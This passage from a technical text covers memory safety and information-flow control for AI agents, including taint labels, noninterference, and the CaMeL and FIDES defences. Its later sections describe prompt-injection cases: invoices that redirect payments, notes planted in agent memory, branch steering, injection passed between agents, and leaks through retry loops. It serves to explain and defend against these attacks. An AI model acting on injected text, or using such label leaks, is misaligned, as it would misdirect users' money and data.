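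Bytecode verification does part of the memory-safety checking before the program runs. Java programs arrive as bytecode, instructions for a simple virtual machine, and the sender may have produced them without a Java compiler. The verifier therefore works out the type of every value at every instruction in each method, using the same kind of coarse descriptions as the sign analysis of the invoice amount. Where two paths meet, it keeps only what is true on both. It rejects code that treats a number as a reference or jumps into the middle of an instruction. The virtual machine still checks array bounds, null references and many type conversions at run time.

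WebAssembly, a bytecode format to which C programs can also compile, gives a weaker guarantee inside the program. Its checker verifies types and jumps, but its run-time check only keeps ordinary memory accesses within one large block. A C parser compiled to WebAssembly could still overwrite a taint mark in its own block, though it could not reach the harness's memory. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent runtime, IronClaw, that uses WebAssembly in this way to confine many of its tools.

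Rust needs no garbage collector because its types record what owns each value. Every value has one owner, and the compiler inserts code to free the value when the owner goes out of scope. Passing the value to another function can transfer ownership, and the compiler then rejects any use of the old variable. In the second example, `drop(page)` would replace `free(page)`, and the next line would not compile. Code can also borrow a value without owning it. The compiler allows either several readers or one writer at a time, and no borrowed reference may outlive the value. In safe Rust, these rules prevent temporal errors and data races (unsynchronised accesses to the same memory by several threads, at least one of them a write) before the program runs. Most array accesses still need a bounds check at run time.

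In 2018 Ralf Jung and colleagues proved that these rules ensure memory safety in a simplified version of Rust. But programmers can handle raw pointers in blocks marked `unsafe`, or call a C library. The compiler cannot guarantee that such code is memory-safe, and a mistake in it can corrupt memory that safe code uses.

### Separation logic for existing C code

C libraries that developers cannot replace need a proof of their own. Separation logic makes such proofs manageable by keeping track of which memory a piece of code owns. The assertion $p \mapsto v$ means that the code owns the cell at address $p$ and that the cell contains $v$. $P * Q$ means that $P$ and $Q$ describe separate parts of memory. A statement $\{P\}\,c\,\{Q\}$ means that if $P$ holds beforehand, the command $c$ runs without a memory error, and $Q$ holds if it finishes. Two of the basic rules are

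$$\{p \mapsto v\}\;\; {*p} = w \;\;\{p \mapsto w\} \qquad\qquad \{p \mapsto v\}\;\; \mathrm{free}(p) \;\;\{\mathrm{emp}\}$$

where $\mathrm{emp}$ stands for owning nothing. After `free`, the code no longer owns the cell, so no rule permits another access and a use after free has no proof. The spatial error fails for a similar reason. The array `name` provides 32 cells, so a proof of the loop would have to show that $i < 32$, which is impossible while $n$ can be any number. If the developer adds a line that rejects files with $n > 32$, the proof goes through, and the program needs no bounds check on each access.

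The logic also has a "frame rule":

$$\frac{\{P\}\; c\; \{Q\}}{\{P * R\}\; c\; \{Q * R\}}$$

The frame rule applies as long as $c$ does not assign to variables that $R$ mentions. If $P$ describes the parser's buffers and $R$ describes the ledger lock and the taint marks, then a proof that mentions only the buffers also shows that the parser leaves the lock and the marks unchanged, as the deadlock and taint proofs require.

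### A proof for liblzma

*Agent-Driven Verification of Memory Safety for liblzma Decoder Components with VST* (Shlyakhtun, Gryzlov and colleagues, August 2026) reports a proof of memory safety for part of liblzma, a widely used C library that unpacks compressed files. For each function, people wrote and approved a contract that lists what the caller must provide and what the function delivers. Agents running in Claude Code then wrote the proofs, and the proof assistant Rocq checked them. The proofs cover 22 decoder functions and five supporting functions.

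The hardest function, `lzma_decode`, has 338 lines of C, and its proof has 183,268 lines. The agents needed 1,595 sessions over 70 days. Repeated blocks make up about 42% of the lines in the 28 files that hold most of the proof. Shlyakhtun and colleagues had no records of the hours people spent and no comparison with a team working without agents, so the project shows that agents can carry out a proof of this size but not that they save labour.

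The agents were not allowed to change a contract. An agent that could do so could make any proof easy by requiring the caller to meet an impossible condition. When one agent got stuck, it found that a loop's description allowed a state that the C code could never reach. It explained why and proposed a stricter description, which a person approved. Agents then repaired the proof at nine places that had to establish the new condition. The contracts can still be wrong. Before the main proof, the team compared its mathematical model of the decoder with recorded runs of the C program, which led to six corrections.

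Each theorem holds only if the caller meets the function's contract and the functions it relies on meet theirs. For example, the proof assumes that `malloc` and `free` behave as their contracts say. It does not show that a function finishes or that separately maintained contracts fit together. It also excludes all compression code and the code that reads the `.xz` container and checks its integrity, although this container code handles untrusted files too.

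The verified C code differs slightly from the released liblzma because the team rewrote some jumps and assignments that the verification tool cannot handle. Applying the theorems to the released library requires showing that both versions behave the same. The team also found a fault in the code. When a caller supplies no input in one mode, the code adds zero to a null pointer, which is undefined in the C standard they used. The contract for `lzma_decode` excludes this call, so the theorem does not cover a program that makes it.

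### Proofs for code that agents write

Some agents write native code themselves, including kernels, the small programs that run on graphics processors. *ProofWright* (Chatterjee, Zagieboylo and colleagues, 2025) uses an agent to add contracts and hints to kernels written in NVIDIA's CUDA language, and the VerCors verifier checks the result. VerCors uses a version of separation logic in which a thread must own all of a memory location to write to it, but can read it with any fraction of the ownership. The fractions never add up to more than one, so no thread can write to a location while another uses it. The proof therefore excludes data races as well as memory errors.

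For 100 kernels by Claude Sonnet 4, this produced 74 proofs, and the whole process took about three minutes per kernel. The other 26 kernels are not necessarily faulty. In 17 cases the automatic solver behind VerCors failed unpredictably, sometimes on correct code, and in nine the agent did not find a suitable contract or the verifier lacked a feature. Tests can miss errors that these proofs rule out. One kernel by GPT-4.1 passed repeated unit tests despite a data race that occurred only when the input length was not a multiple of four. A memory-safe kernel can still return wrong numbers, and only 14 of the 74 also had a proof that they compute the right function.

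Chatterjee and colleagues claim that they "will never verify a program that is incorrect". This claim holds only relative to the contracts, which the agent itself writes. The agent often fixes the number of threads in a contract. If it specifies 256 per block, for instance, the proof does not apply to a launch with 128. The team checked that the contracts were not trivially impossible to satisfy, which is a much lighter check than the human approval in the liblzma project.

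### Which parts need a proof

If the invoice assistant's harness is written in Python, the language makes its loops, ledger and payment code memory-safe. The remaining risk is in the native code that the harness runs on or calls, such as the interpreter, the PDF parser and any compiled module that an agent writes. Parsers deserve the most attention because strangers choose their input.

An agent that seems memory-safe can depend on a large amount of native code. Claude Code runs on Bun, a JavaScript runtime that consisted largely of 535,496 lines of Zig, a language in which programmers free memory by hand. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) lists faults that the Bun team fixed in a single release, including several uses after free, a double free and an out-of-bounds write in the code that sends network packets. The team had already been running a memory-error detector on every commit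 and continuously testing the runtime with random programs. Sumner, who created Bun and works at Anthropic, then had Claude translate the Zig code into Rust in 11 days. Willison (2026) found the names of 563 Rust source files inside his installed copy of Claude Code, which shows that the Rust version had reached users by July 2026.

The translation does not make all of Bun memory-safe. It left in place the C++ code, which makes up about 20% of Bun, and large C and C++ libraries such as the JavaScript engine. The new Rust code also follows the old code closely, and the number of `unsafe` blocks is to be reduced later. In one place, the Rust code passed an object to a C library and then freed it while the library still needed it. The library would have used the freed memory and then freed it again. This code compiled, but a second instance of Claude caught the error in review. Sumner does not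 report that anyone exploited any of the faults, so they are evidence of memory errors in agent runtimes but not of attacks that use them.

OpenAI's rewrite of its coding agent Codex CLI is weaker evidence, because the old version was in TypeScript, which is already memory-safe apart from native add-ons. According to heise online's *Security and performance*, the first reason the maintainers gave was to spare users from installing Node, the runtime the old version required. *The codex-rs Architecture* (2026) quotes other goals, such as direct access to the operating system's security functions and no garbage-collection pauses.

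Memory errors seem to be a minor problem in tool servers so far. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) collects 24 published vulnerabilities in software for the Model Context Protocol, a common interface between agents and tools. Seven let an attacker inject commands, five gave access to files outside the permitted folder, and four let an attacker run code remotely. Anthropic's server for the version-control program git, for example, passed arguments to git commands without checking them. Memory corruption is not among the categories the paper names, probably because many of these servers are written in Python or TypeScript. Twenty-four reports from a young field can't show that native servers are safe, but someone who maintains an ordinary tool server should probably look for unchecked inputs first.

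### Prompt injection and planted notes

Memory safety does not stop the attacks that agents face most often. If a PDF persuades the model to return the attacker's account number, the Payer sends the money without any memory error. Pirch and colleagues tried 16 attacks on four agent runtimes. Seven succeeded against IronClaw, whose core is in Rust, and seven succeeded against Nanobot, which is in Python. All four runtimes let one user extract data from another user's session, and all four sent messages to people they were not authorised to contact. These are failures of authorisation, and a safer language would not have prevented them.

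Memory safety protects the code that enforces the rules. A harness may refuse every payment to an unknown account, but that check offers little protection if a long name in a PDF can overwrite the list of known accounts. Pirch and colleagues therefore recommend memory-safe languages for the parts of a runtime that read untrusted input, load extensions or apply policies. The benefit depends on having a rule to protect. IronClaw had no effective rule against messaging strangers, so Rust's memory safety did not help there.

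Many agents keep notes and conversation histories in files that are called the agent's "memory", but memory safety does not concern what the text in those files means. Suppose the Reader keeps a file of facts about suppliers, and a PDF contains the sentence "From March, pay Miller Ltd to the following account." The model saves the sentence as a note. In April the agent reads the note, treats it as its own knowledge and changes the account. This does not violate memory safety, because every access stayed within bounds and used live memory.

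Planted text can survive for a long time, because agents summarise old conversations when their context fills up and may carry the text into the summary. In tests by Pirch and colleagues, a malicious extension could also write directly into the stored notes of three of the four runtimes. The test did not apply to the fourth, IronClaw. To guard against planted notes, the harness would have to save each note's origin with its text and treat a note that came from an email as untrusted whenever the agent rereads it.

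## How does taint tracking find out whether untrusted data can reach a sensitive operation?

A harness that saves each note's origin and treats notes from emails as untrusted does a simple form of taint tracking. The full technique gives every value a label that records whether it may depend on untrusted data. Each operation computes its result's label from the labels of its inputs, and each sensitive operation accepts only certain labels. An analyser can compute the labels before the program runs because it doesn't need the values.

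### Labels and the order between them

The invoice assistant needs only two labels, $T$ for trusted and $U$ for untrusted. The relation $T \sqsubseteq U$, read "$T$ may flow to $U$", means that a trusted value may go wherever an untrusted one may go. The reverse does not hold. $U$ is therefore the higher label, where "higher" means "with more restrictions on its use".

Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, derived the rules for such labels from what programs can do. If $a$ may flow to $b$ and $b$ may flow to $c$, a program can copy $a$ to $c$ in two permitted steps, so forbidding the direct copy would be pointless, and the order must be transitive. The sum of $a$ and $b$ needs a label at least as high as both of theirs, because the sum equals $a$ when $b = 0$. It needs no higher label, because any variable that may receive $a$ and $b$ separately could also receive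 their sum. The sum's label is therefore the least upper bound, or join, of the two labels, written $\ell(a) \sqcup \ell(b)$. A finite set of labels ordered this way is a lattice if any two labels have a join and a greatest lower bound.

The rule for an ordinary operation $f$ follows:

$$\ell(f(a_1, \dots, a_n)) = \ell(a_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \ell(a_n)$$

With two labels, one untrusted input makes the result untrusted. This rule is the same for every $f$, so `inv.amount - inv.amount` is untrusted even though it is always zero. Constants in the program text have the label $T$.

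An agent that also handles secrets needs a second pair of labels, $P$ for public and $S$ for secret, with $P \sqsubseteq S$. The two pairs combine into a product lattice with four labels, where

$$(c, i) \sqsubseteq (c', i') \quad\text{exactly when}\quad c \sqsubseteq c' \text{ and } i \sqsubseteq i'.$$

A supplier's bank details in the company's own registry might be labeled $(S, T)$, for secret and trusted, and a stranger's email $(P, U)$, for public and untrusted. Neither label may flow to the other. Text that quotes both gets their join, $(S, U)$, which is the highest label. With the product, each operation can have its own limit. `send_payment` may receive secrets but must receive only trusted data, so its limit is $(S, T)$. An email to a stranger may repeat untrusted text but must not contain secrets, so its limit is $(P, U)$.

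*Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) points out a difference between integrity (whether data are trustworthy) and confidentiality (whether they are secret), which otherwise look symmetric here. A program can damage integrity without any outside influence, by computing something wrongly. If a bug in the Clerk multiplies every amount by ten, the amounts are wrong but their labels stay the same.

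### From the mail to the payment

The invoice assistant has one source, `fetch_mail`, and one sink, `send_payment`, whose two arguments must both have the label $T$. Other agents have more sources and sinks. DeepClause's *Static taint analysis for LLM agents* describes an analyser for a small Prolog-based agent language. The analyser's sources include everything the user types or a model returns. Its sinks include the system prompt, which contains the standing instructions that a model reads first, and tools that execute code.

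In the following derivation, line 3 counts as an ordinary function of the fixed instruction and the PDF's text. (A real model call may also read an earlier conversation with taint of its own.)

| Line | Step | Label |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `mail = fetch_mail()` | `mail` is $U$, because `fetch_mail` is a source |
| 2 | `text = parse_pdf(mail.attachment)` | `text` is $U$ |
| 3 | `inv = extract("Extract …", text)` | `inv` is $T \sqcup U = U$ |
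| 4, 5 | Reader sends `inv` to Clerk | the Clerk's copy is $U$ |
| 6 | `ledger.add(inv)` | `ledger` is $T \sqcup U = U$ |
| 7, 9 | Clerk sends `inv` to Payer | the Payer's copy is $U$ |
| 10 | `send_payment(inv.account, inv.amount)` | both arguments are $U$, but the limit is $T$ |

Since $U \sqsubseteq T$ is false, the analyser rejects the program at line 10. It can also print the path from `fetch_mail` to `send_payment`, so the developer can see where they could add a check. The analyser would reject the program even if every invoice the company received were genuine.

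If the analyser keeps one label for the whole ledger, a single invoice from the mail makes every entry untrusted at line 6, including those a bookkeeper typed in. A separate label for each entry would avoid this but require more work from the analyser.

### Branches and loops

After an `if`, a variable may hold a value from either branch, so the analyser joins the labels from both. If one branch sets `account` from the mail and the other sets it to a constant, `account` is untrusted afterwards.

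Loops need repeated passes, because taint can take several rounds to arrive. Suppose a Payer holds back each payment for two rounds so that someone can still cancel it, and starts with the landlord's account in both places:

```
held = rent_account
next = rent_account
while true:
    inv = receive_invoice()
    send_payment(held, 100)
    held = next
    next = inv.account
```

In the first two rounds, the agent pays the landlord. In the third, it pays an account whose number came from the mail, so a test that stopped after two rounds would find nothing wrong.

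The analyser starts with the labels before the loop, where `held` and `next` are both $T$. After one pass through the body, it gets $T$ for `held` and $U$ for `next`. It joins these with the starting labels, because a round may be the first or may follow another, and goes through the body again. This time `held` also becomes $U$. Another pass changes nothing, so the analyser has reached a fixed point, and its labels are valid at the start of every round. Because `held` is $U$ at the payment, the analyser raises the alarm.

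The computation ends because joins only raise labels and the lattice is finite. With $n$ variables and two labels, each pass except the last raises at least one variable from $T$ to $U$, so $n + 1$ passes are enough. The same method handles messages between agents if the analyser gives each queue a label. DeepClause's analyser, which is about 200 lines long, also repeats its rules until nothing new becomes tainted. But it treats each clause of the agent's program separately, so it can miss taint that passes from one clause to another.

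The repetition is necessary only if the analyser has to infer the labels. In *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977), programmers declare a label for every variable, and the compiler checks each statement once against the declarations. Because permitted flows are transitive, a sequence of permitted steps is also permitted. In the delayed payment loop, a programmer who declared `held` as $T$ and `next` as $U$ would get an error at `held = next`.

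### A trusted registry and an untrusted key

The obvious repair for the invoice assistant is to ignore the account number in the PDF and look up the supplier in a registry that only the company's staff can edit:

```
account = lookup_vendor(inv.payee)
receipt = send_payment(account, inv.amount)
```

Every account number in the registry is trusted, but the name used as the key came from the mail. Reading an array element raises the same problem, and Denning and Denning's rule gives `a[i]` the join of the labels of `a` and `i`. For the lookup this gives $T \sqcup U = U$, so the analyser still rejects the program.

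The result of a lookup must carry the key's label as well as the table's, even when the table is a registry to which an attacker cannot add accounts. Otherwise, a program could remove the untrusted label from any value by rebuilding it from trusted data. Suppose a trusted table `digits` holds the ten digits in order. A program could go through the attacker's account number and append `digits[d]` for each digit `d`. The result would be the attacker's account number, but it would be labelled trusted because every character came from a trusted table.

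Unlike the table in `digits`, the one in `lookup_vendor` contains only the accounts of registered suppliers, so any key returns one of those accounts or an error. If the company considers that good enough, the developer can declare `lookup_vendor` a sanitiser, a function whose result the analyser treats as trusted even if its input was not. This declaration, called an endorsement, is a policy decision that no analyser could derive from the code. The analyser also doesn't check that the sanitiser works correctly, so the proof would still succeed if `lookup_vendor` returned the key itself whenever it found no match.

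The analyser still rejects the program because the amount comes straight from the mail. A second sanitiser could return the amount only if the company has an open order with this supplier for exactly that sum. With both sanitisers in place, the analyser accepts the program, which proves that accounts and amounts reach `send_payment` only through these two functions. Somebody who can send mail may still choose which open order the company pays next. But the analyser does catch the common mistake of checking one field and then using another. If the program looks up the payee but then pays `inv.account`, the analyser rejects it because that field is still $U$.

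A sanitiser makes data safe for a particular sink. Removing control characters from a supplier's name may make it safe to print in a report, but it does not make the name any safer to use as a key for payments. In the product lattice, an endorsement should also leave the confidentiality part unchanged, so that a registry account is relabelled $(S, T)$ without becoming public. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) prove in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* that endorsing data in their agent language, LLMbda, preserves the guarantee about secrets. DeepClause's analyser does not yet recognise sanitisers, so it warns about a flow even after a developer has added a proper check.

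### Flows through branches

So far a value became tainted only by receiving data from another value, which is an explicit flow. The mail can also influence a payment without any of its data reaching the sink:

```
1  account = miller_account
2  if inv.payee == "Jones":
3      account = jones_account
4  send_payment(account, 100)
```

Both account numbers and the amount are constants, so an analyser that follows only explicit flows labels everything at line 4 as trusted and accepts the program. But the name in the mail determines who gets the money, which Denning calls an implicit flow. This flow occurs whether or not line 3 runs, because the value of `account` depends on the name even when it stays unchanged.

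This program is equivalent to a registry lookup with two entries. An analyser that ignores implicit flows would therefore reject `lookup_vendor(inv.payee)` but accept the same lookup written as a chain of `if` statements. A program with enough branches can also copy arbitrary data, for example by testing each digit of the attacker's account number against 0 to 9 and appending the matching constant.

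To catch implicit flows, the analyser keeps one more label, $pc$ (for "program counter", the position that the run has reached). It starts as $T$. Inside both branches of an `if`, and inside the body of a loop, the analyser raises it to $pc \sqcup \ell(\text{condition})$. An assignment `x = e` then gives `x` the label

$$\ell(x) = pc \sqcup \ell(e),$$

and a call to a sink needs a $pc$ within the sink's limit, just like its arguments. At line 3, $pc$ is $U$, so `account` becomes $U$ and the analyser rejects line 4. After the `if`, $pc$ returns to its old label. Sabelfeld and Myers explain why this is safe. The program reaches the next statement whichever way the test goes, so reaching it reveals nothing about the condition.

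Exceptions are harder because they create branches that the source code does not show. In an example by Denning and Denning, a program repeatedly adds a secret number $x$ to a sum and writes the number of rounds to a public file, until the sum overflows and the program stops. Anyone can estimate $x$ by dividing the largest number the machine can store by the last entry in the file. Denning and Denning's basic rules accept this program. They suggest switching off all exceptions but those with an explicit handler, which the compiler can check like any other branch. Their method does not cover some flows, such as those through a program's running time or power consumption.

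Tracking implicit flows in an agent soon raises more alarms than a developer wants. Suppose the Payer skips invoices with negative amounts, which the sign analysis needed for its proof. The payment is then inside an `if` whose condition came from the mail, so the analyser rejects it even if the account and the amount are constants. Developers can endorse the condition, but they will have to do this for almost every decision the agent takes after reading its mail. This is probably why some tools don't fully track implicit flows. The propagation rules that DeepClause describes cover only explicit flows, apart from a warning when a model call inherits a tainted conversation. FIDES, an agent defence discussed by Garby and colleagues, deliberately does not track secrets through branches.

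### Noninterference

An analyser that follows only explicit flows can prove taint safety for the four-line program, even though the mail controls its payments. Such a proof does not establish noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer (1982) define in *Security Policies and Security Models* for a machine that several users share. The machine starts in state $s_0$. $\mathrm{do}(s, u, c)$ gives the next state when user $u$ issues command $c$ in state $s$, and $\mathrm{out}(s, u)$ gives what user $u$ sees in state $s$.

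Let $w$ be a sequence of commands, each with the user who issued it, and let $[\![w]\!]_u$ be what $u$ sees after the machine has carried out all of $w$. For a group of users $G$, let $P_G(w)$ be the same sequence without the commands that members of $G$ issued. The group $G$ does not interfere with a group $G'$ if

$$[\![w]\!]_u = [\![P_G(w)]\!]_u \qquad \text{for all } w \text{ and all } u \in G'.$$

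In other words, the members of $G'$ never see anything that they would not also have seen if $G$ had done nothing. For a deterministic program with trusted inputs $t$ and untrusted inputs $x$, the corresponding condition is

$$\mathrm{obs}(t, x) = \mathrm{obs}(t, x') \qquad \text{for all } t, x, x',$$

where $\mathrm{obs}$ is what trusted observers see of the run. The four-line program violates it. With the same trusted inputs, an invoice from Miller leads to a payment to Miller, and an invoice from Jones leads to a payment to Jones.

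If $G$ is the people who send mail and $G'$ is the bank, no useful invoice assistant satisfies the definition. Without the mail there would be no payment, however carefully the program checks the account and the amount. Proofs about such programs therefore need endorsements or a different observer. For example, we can reasonably require that mail not affect what staff see in the supplier registry. The invoice assistant meets this requirement because none of its lines writes to the registry.

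The definition also depends on where the untrusted data enter. Goguen and Meseguer implicitly assume that the initial state contains no sensitive information and that all such information arrives through commands. *Noninterference*, a set of lecture slides from Purdue University, states this assumption explicitly. For integrity, the initial state must contain nothing untrusted. An agent that starts each morning with notes from yesterday's mail breaks this assumption, because deleting today's commands does not delete the notes.

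Noninterference compares two runs, so no single log can show whether a program satisfies it. Suppose the log of the four-line program shows an invoice from Miller, followed by a payment of 100 to Miller. A program that always pays Miller 100, whatever the mail contains, would produce the same log, and that program satisfies noninterference. The two programs differ only in what they would have done with other mail. More detailed logs do not help. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) surveys records of agent runs that include retrieved documents, tool calls, memory operations and messages between agents. Even a complete record of this kind describes only one run, and if that run skips line 3, the record contains no trace of it. A proof has to cover all pairs of runs, as a static analysis does when it labels both branches.

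Denning and Denning showed that their compiler accepts a program only if the policy permits every flow, as their rules define it, that the program's statements specify. According to Sabelfeld (2009), Dennis Volpano, Geoffrey Smith and Cynthia Irvine first proved the static check sound in 1996. Their theorem relates the labels to what the program computes, for a small language without exceptions or concurrent processes.

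### Labels carried at run time

The harness can attach labels to the actual values and update them during the run, instead of computing them in advance. This lets it use information that a static analyser lacks. For example, `fetch_mail` returns messages from both strangers and the company's bookkeeper. A static analysis has to label every message $U$ because the same line of code fetches them all, but the harness can label a message $T$ at run time if it has verified that the bookkeeper sent it.

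But the harness follows only one path at a time, and implicit flows also depend on the path not taken. Denning illustrates this with a program by J. S. Fenton. Here `a` is an untrusted true-or-false value from the mail:

```
b = false
c = false
if not a: c = true
if not c: b = true
```

Suppose the harness joins the label of each condition to every assignment that actually happens under it.

| Step | If `a` is true | If `a` is false |
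|---|---|---|
| `if not a: c = true` | skipped, so `c` stays false with label $T$ | `c` becomes true with label $U$ |
| `if not c: b = true` | `b` becomes true with label $T$ | skipped, so `b` stays false with label $T$ |

In both cases `b` ends up equal to `a` and its label is $T$, so the harness has labelled an untrusted value as trusted. A static analyser avoids this mistake because it finds an assignment to `c` under an untrusted condition, labels `c` as $U$ for all runs, and then does the same for `b`.

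Garby and colleagues reproduced the flaw in the interpreter of CaMeL, a defence from Google in which a model writes a program and the interpreter runs it with labels attached. In their example, an injected instruction is meant to reveal whether a customer's balance exceeds a threshold. CaMeL blocks an email sent directly under that condition, but allows it when the program first passes the answer through two variables, as Fenton's program does.

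There are several remedies, each with a drawback. Denning proposed that a compiler find the variables that a skipped branch could have changed and insert instructions that raise their labels anyway, but this requires static analysis. Another is to leave $pc$ high for the rest of the run once it has risen, which causes what Sabelfeld and Myers call "label creep". An agent that makes one decision based on an email in its first minute would label everything it does afterwards as untrusted. Garby and colleagues use a rule by Thomas Austin and Cormac Flanagan that stops the run when code under a high condition tries to change something with a lower label. In Fenton's program, this rule would stop every run in which `a` is false, even if nothing ever used `b`.

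Stopping a run can itself reveal a secret. Denning described a program that deliberately commits $x$ violations, where $x$ is a confidential number, so that its owner can read $x$ from the record of aborted operations. Garby and colleagues found a similar weakness in CaMeL, whose interpreter runs inside an ordinary retry loop without labels. Each attempt reveals one bit (whether the policy blocked it), so an attacker who can steer the retries can extract a whole secret. A program that passes a static check attempts no forbidden operations, so it cannot leak in this way.

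Like other monitors, run-time labels take effect late. They stop the invoice assistant at line 10, when the Clerk has already entered the invoice in the ledger and is waiting at line 8 for a receipt. If the harness only cancels the payment, the receipt never arrives and the Clerk is stuck, as it would be in a deadlock. The harness therefore needs a way to notify the Clerk of the refusal and correct the ledger.

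Static labels raise false alarms over runs that cannot happen, as the sign analysis did with the `refund` flag. Shared functions cause more trouble in practice. If an analyser keeps a single label for the input of a sorting function, one call with data from the mail makes it treat the results of all other calls as untrusted. For functions whose results depend only on their arguments and on constants, Denning and Denning avoid this by computing the label separately for each call.

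Run-time labels cause neither of these alarms. They still cause one for `inv.amount - inv.amount`, and for a bookkeeper's entry in a ledger that has one label for everything. They also use some time and memory at every operation, whereas static labels use none while the program runs.

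## How can an agent read untrusted text and still be taint-safe?

The invoice assistant gives its model a fixed instruction and one PDF at a time, so a PDF can taint only the invoice that the model extracts from it. Many agents instead keep one long conversation, to which the harness adds every request, every answer from the model and every tool result. Any word of the next answer may depend on any word of that conversation. After the messages $m_1, \dots, m_k$, the answer therefore gets the label

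$$\ell(\text{answer}) = \ell(m_1) \sqcup \dots \sqcup \ell(m_k).$$

Suppose a bookkeeper asks such an agent to check whether Miller Ltd has written and then to pay the rent. The agent reads the mail, which makes the conversation untrusted. When the model then tries to pay the landlord, the harness blocks the payment because the email may have changed what the model wrote, even though the account number came from the bookkeeper. The agent could have paid the rent before reading the mail, but once it has read an email, it can take no sensitive action for the rest of the conversation.

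*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) measured how this rule affects task completion on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in four simulated settings (office work, travel, banking and the chat program Slack), with attacks hidden in the data the agent reads. With GPT-4o, an agent that kept one label for its conversation completed 37.5% of the banking tasks, compared with 98.8% without checks, and 20% of the Slack tasks, compared with 93.3%. Travel was the only setting where the rule did not hurt performance, because the policy let many travel tools run on untrusted data.

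One remedy is to identify which messages influenced an answer and have the model write it again from those messages alone. The designs in this section instead keep untrusted text out of the conversation in which the model chooses tool calls.

### A plan written before the mail arrives

In 2023 Simon Willison proposed dividing the work between two models. A privileged model plans and requests tool calls but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools, so an instruction hidden in the text cannot make it call one. In 2025 Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues turned this idea into CaMeL, a system in which the privileged model writes its whole plan as a Python program.

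Suppose the bookkeeper asks CaMeL to pay the Miller Ltd invoice in today's mail. The privileged model receives this request and the descriptions of the tools, and writes something like this:

```
mail = fetch_mail()
text = parse_pdf(mail.attachment)
inv  = ask_quarantined("Extract payee, account, amount", text, Invoice)
send_payment(lookup_vendor("Miller Ltd"), inv.amount)
```

An interpreter then runs the program. It keeps the mail and the PDF's text in program variables and never passes them to the privileged model. At the third line, the quarantined model reads the text and returns an `Invoice`. The interpreter records which sources each value depends on and checks the arguments of each tool call against a policy before making the call. The account is trusted here because the key for the lookup came from the bookkeeper. Since the amount is untrusted, the policy must either accept untrusted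 amounts or require approval.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls the main guarantee control-flow integrity, which means that the agent's tool calls stay within a plan that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information. If the plan contains an `if`, the mail may determine which branch runs (the paper calls this branch steering), but it cannot add a step to the plan.

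How much control-flow integrity protects the agent depends on the plan. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on this task without policies, the privileged model sometimes wrote a loop with one branch for each tool, which let whoever wrote the file choose any tool. Two attacks succeeded this way, although the agent never left its plan. Control-flow integrity also doesn't protect against a false amount in the PDF, so CaMeL needs the policies as well.

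Because the model plans early, it must write code to parse a tool's result before it has seen one, so developers have to document the structure of every result in advance. If the PDF turns out to need a password from a second email, a plan without that step fails, while an ordinary agent would look for the email.

CaMeL fixes its plan before any untrusted data arrive, but nobody proves anything about that plan. CaMeL applies its labels and policies only while the plan runs. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) explains that Python's dynamic typing, exceptions and reflection (a program's ability to inspect and change itself) make static analysis hard, and recommends a stricter language with bounded loops and simple conditions. Besides the skipped branches and the unlabelled retry loop, Garby and colleagues found that the interpreter drops a value's untrusted label when the program inserts that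 value into a string template.

### When one agent instructs another

Protecting each agent separately is not enough if one agent writes another's instructions. Suppose the Reader and the Clerk both run CaMeL, and the Reader sends the Clerk a plain-English request to enter an invoice, with details from the PDF in the same sentence. The Clerk's privileged model treats that sentence as its user's request, so text that was untrusted in the Reader becomes trusted in the Clerk. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a group of three CaMeL agents and showed that text planted in a database could make one of them send private data to an outsider.

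They also prove that the example generalizes to groups in which a parent agent calls child agents as tools. If any tool in the group returns untrusted data, and users can ask an agent to pass on what a tool returned, then some request makes one agent's plan depend on untrusted data. So a group of two or more such agents lacks control-flow integrity even if each agent has it on its own.

The repair, multi-CaMeL, gives each call to a child agent two arguments:

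```
clerk(message="Enter the attached invoice in the ledger.",
      variables={"invoice": inv})
```

The child's privileged model reads only the message. The interpreter rejects the call if the message depends on any tool result, and variables passed to the child keep their labels. The argument for the whole group is by induction, starting from the first agent. The user's request determines that agent's plan, the plan determines the messages to its children, and each message determines a child's plan. Inserting the children's plans at the calls gives one plan for the group, which untrusted text cannot extend. But multi-CaMeL uses CaMeL's interpreter, which does not detect when a message depends on untrusted data through a skipped branch.

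The original invoice assistant does not have this problem, because its agents exchange `Invoice` records and no agent reads another's message as an instruction.

### Variables that the planner cannot read

FIDES, a system by Costa and colleagues, keeps the ordinary loop in which a model chooses the next call after seeing the last result. Before the harness adds a tool result to the conversation, it compares each field's label with the conversation's label. If the field's label is no higher, the harness leaves the field in place. Otherwise it stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. After `fetch_mail`, the model might see a date and a verified sender, followed by `#fetch_mail_0.body` instead of the message text.

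The model can pass this name to another tool, and the harness replaces the name with the stored value and its label just before the call. A call can therefore be trusted even when one of its arguments is not. For example, a policy for sending messages can require the call and the recipient to be trusted but allow untrusted message text.

This is enough for what Costa and colleagues call data-independent tasks, where the same sequence of tool calls works whatever the data contain. An example is "send my last three emails to Anna". For "send Anna a summary", the planner can have a quarantined model write the summary, which goes into another variable. But "if somebody wants a meeting, put it in my calendar" is data-dependent, because the planner needs information from the mail before it can choose the next call. They count 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks and 44% of its banking tasks as data-dependent.

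For such tasks the planner can inspect a variable, which raises the label of the conversation. To limit the damage, it can first have the quarantined model reduce the email to a yes or no. FIDES makes the type of an answer part of its label, with types ordered by how much information they can carry:

$$\mathrm{bool} \sqsubseteq \mathrm{enum} \sqsubseteq \mathrm{string}$$

A policy can then accept an untrusted Boolean where it would reject an untrusted string.

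FIDES guarantees a property called explicit secrecy. Take any stretch of a run, and let $g$ be the combined effect of its tool calls on the stored data. Write $d_1 =_L d_2$ if two sets of data agree in everything public. The property requires that

$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2).$$

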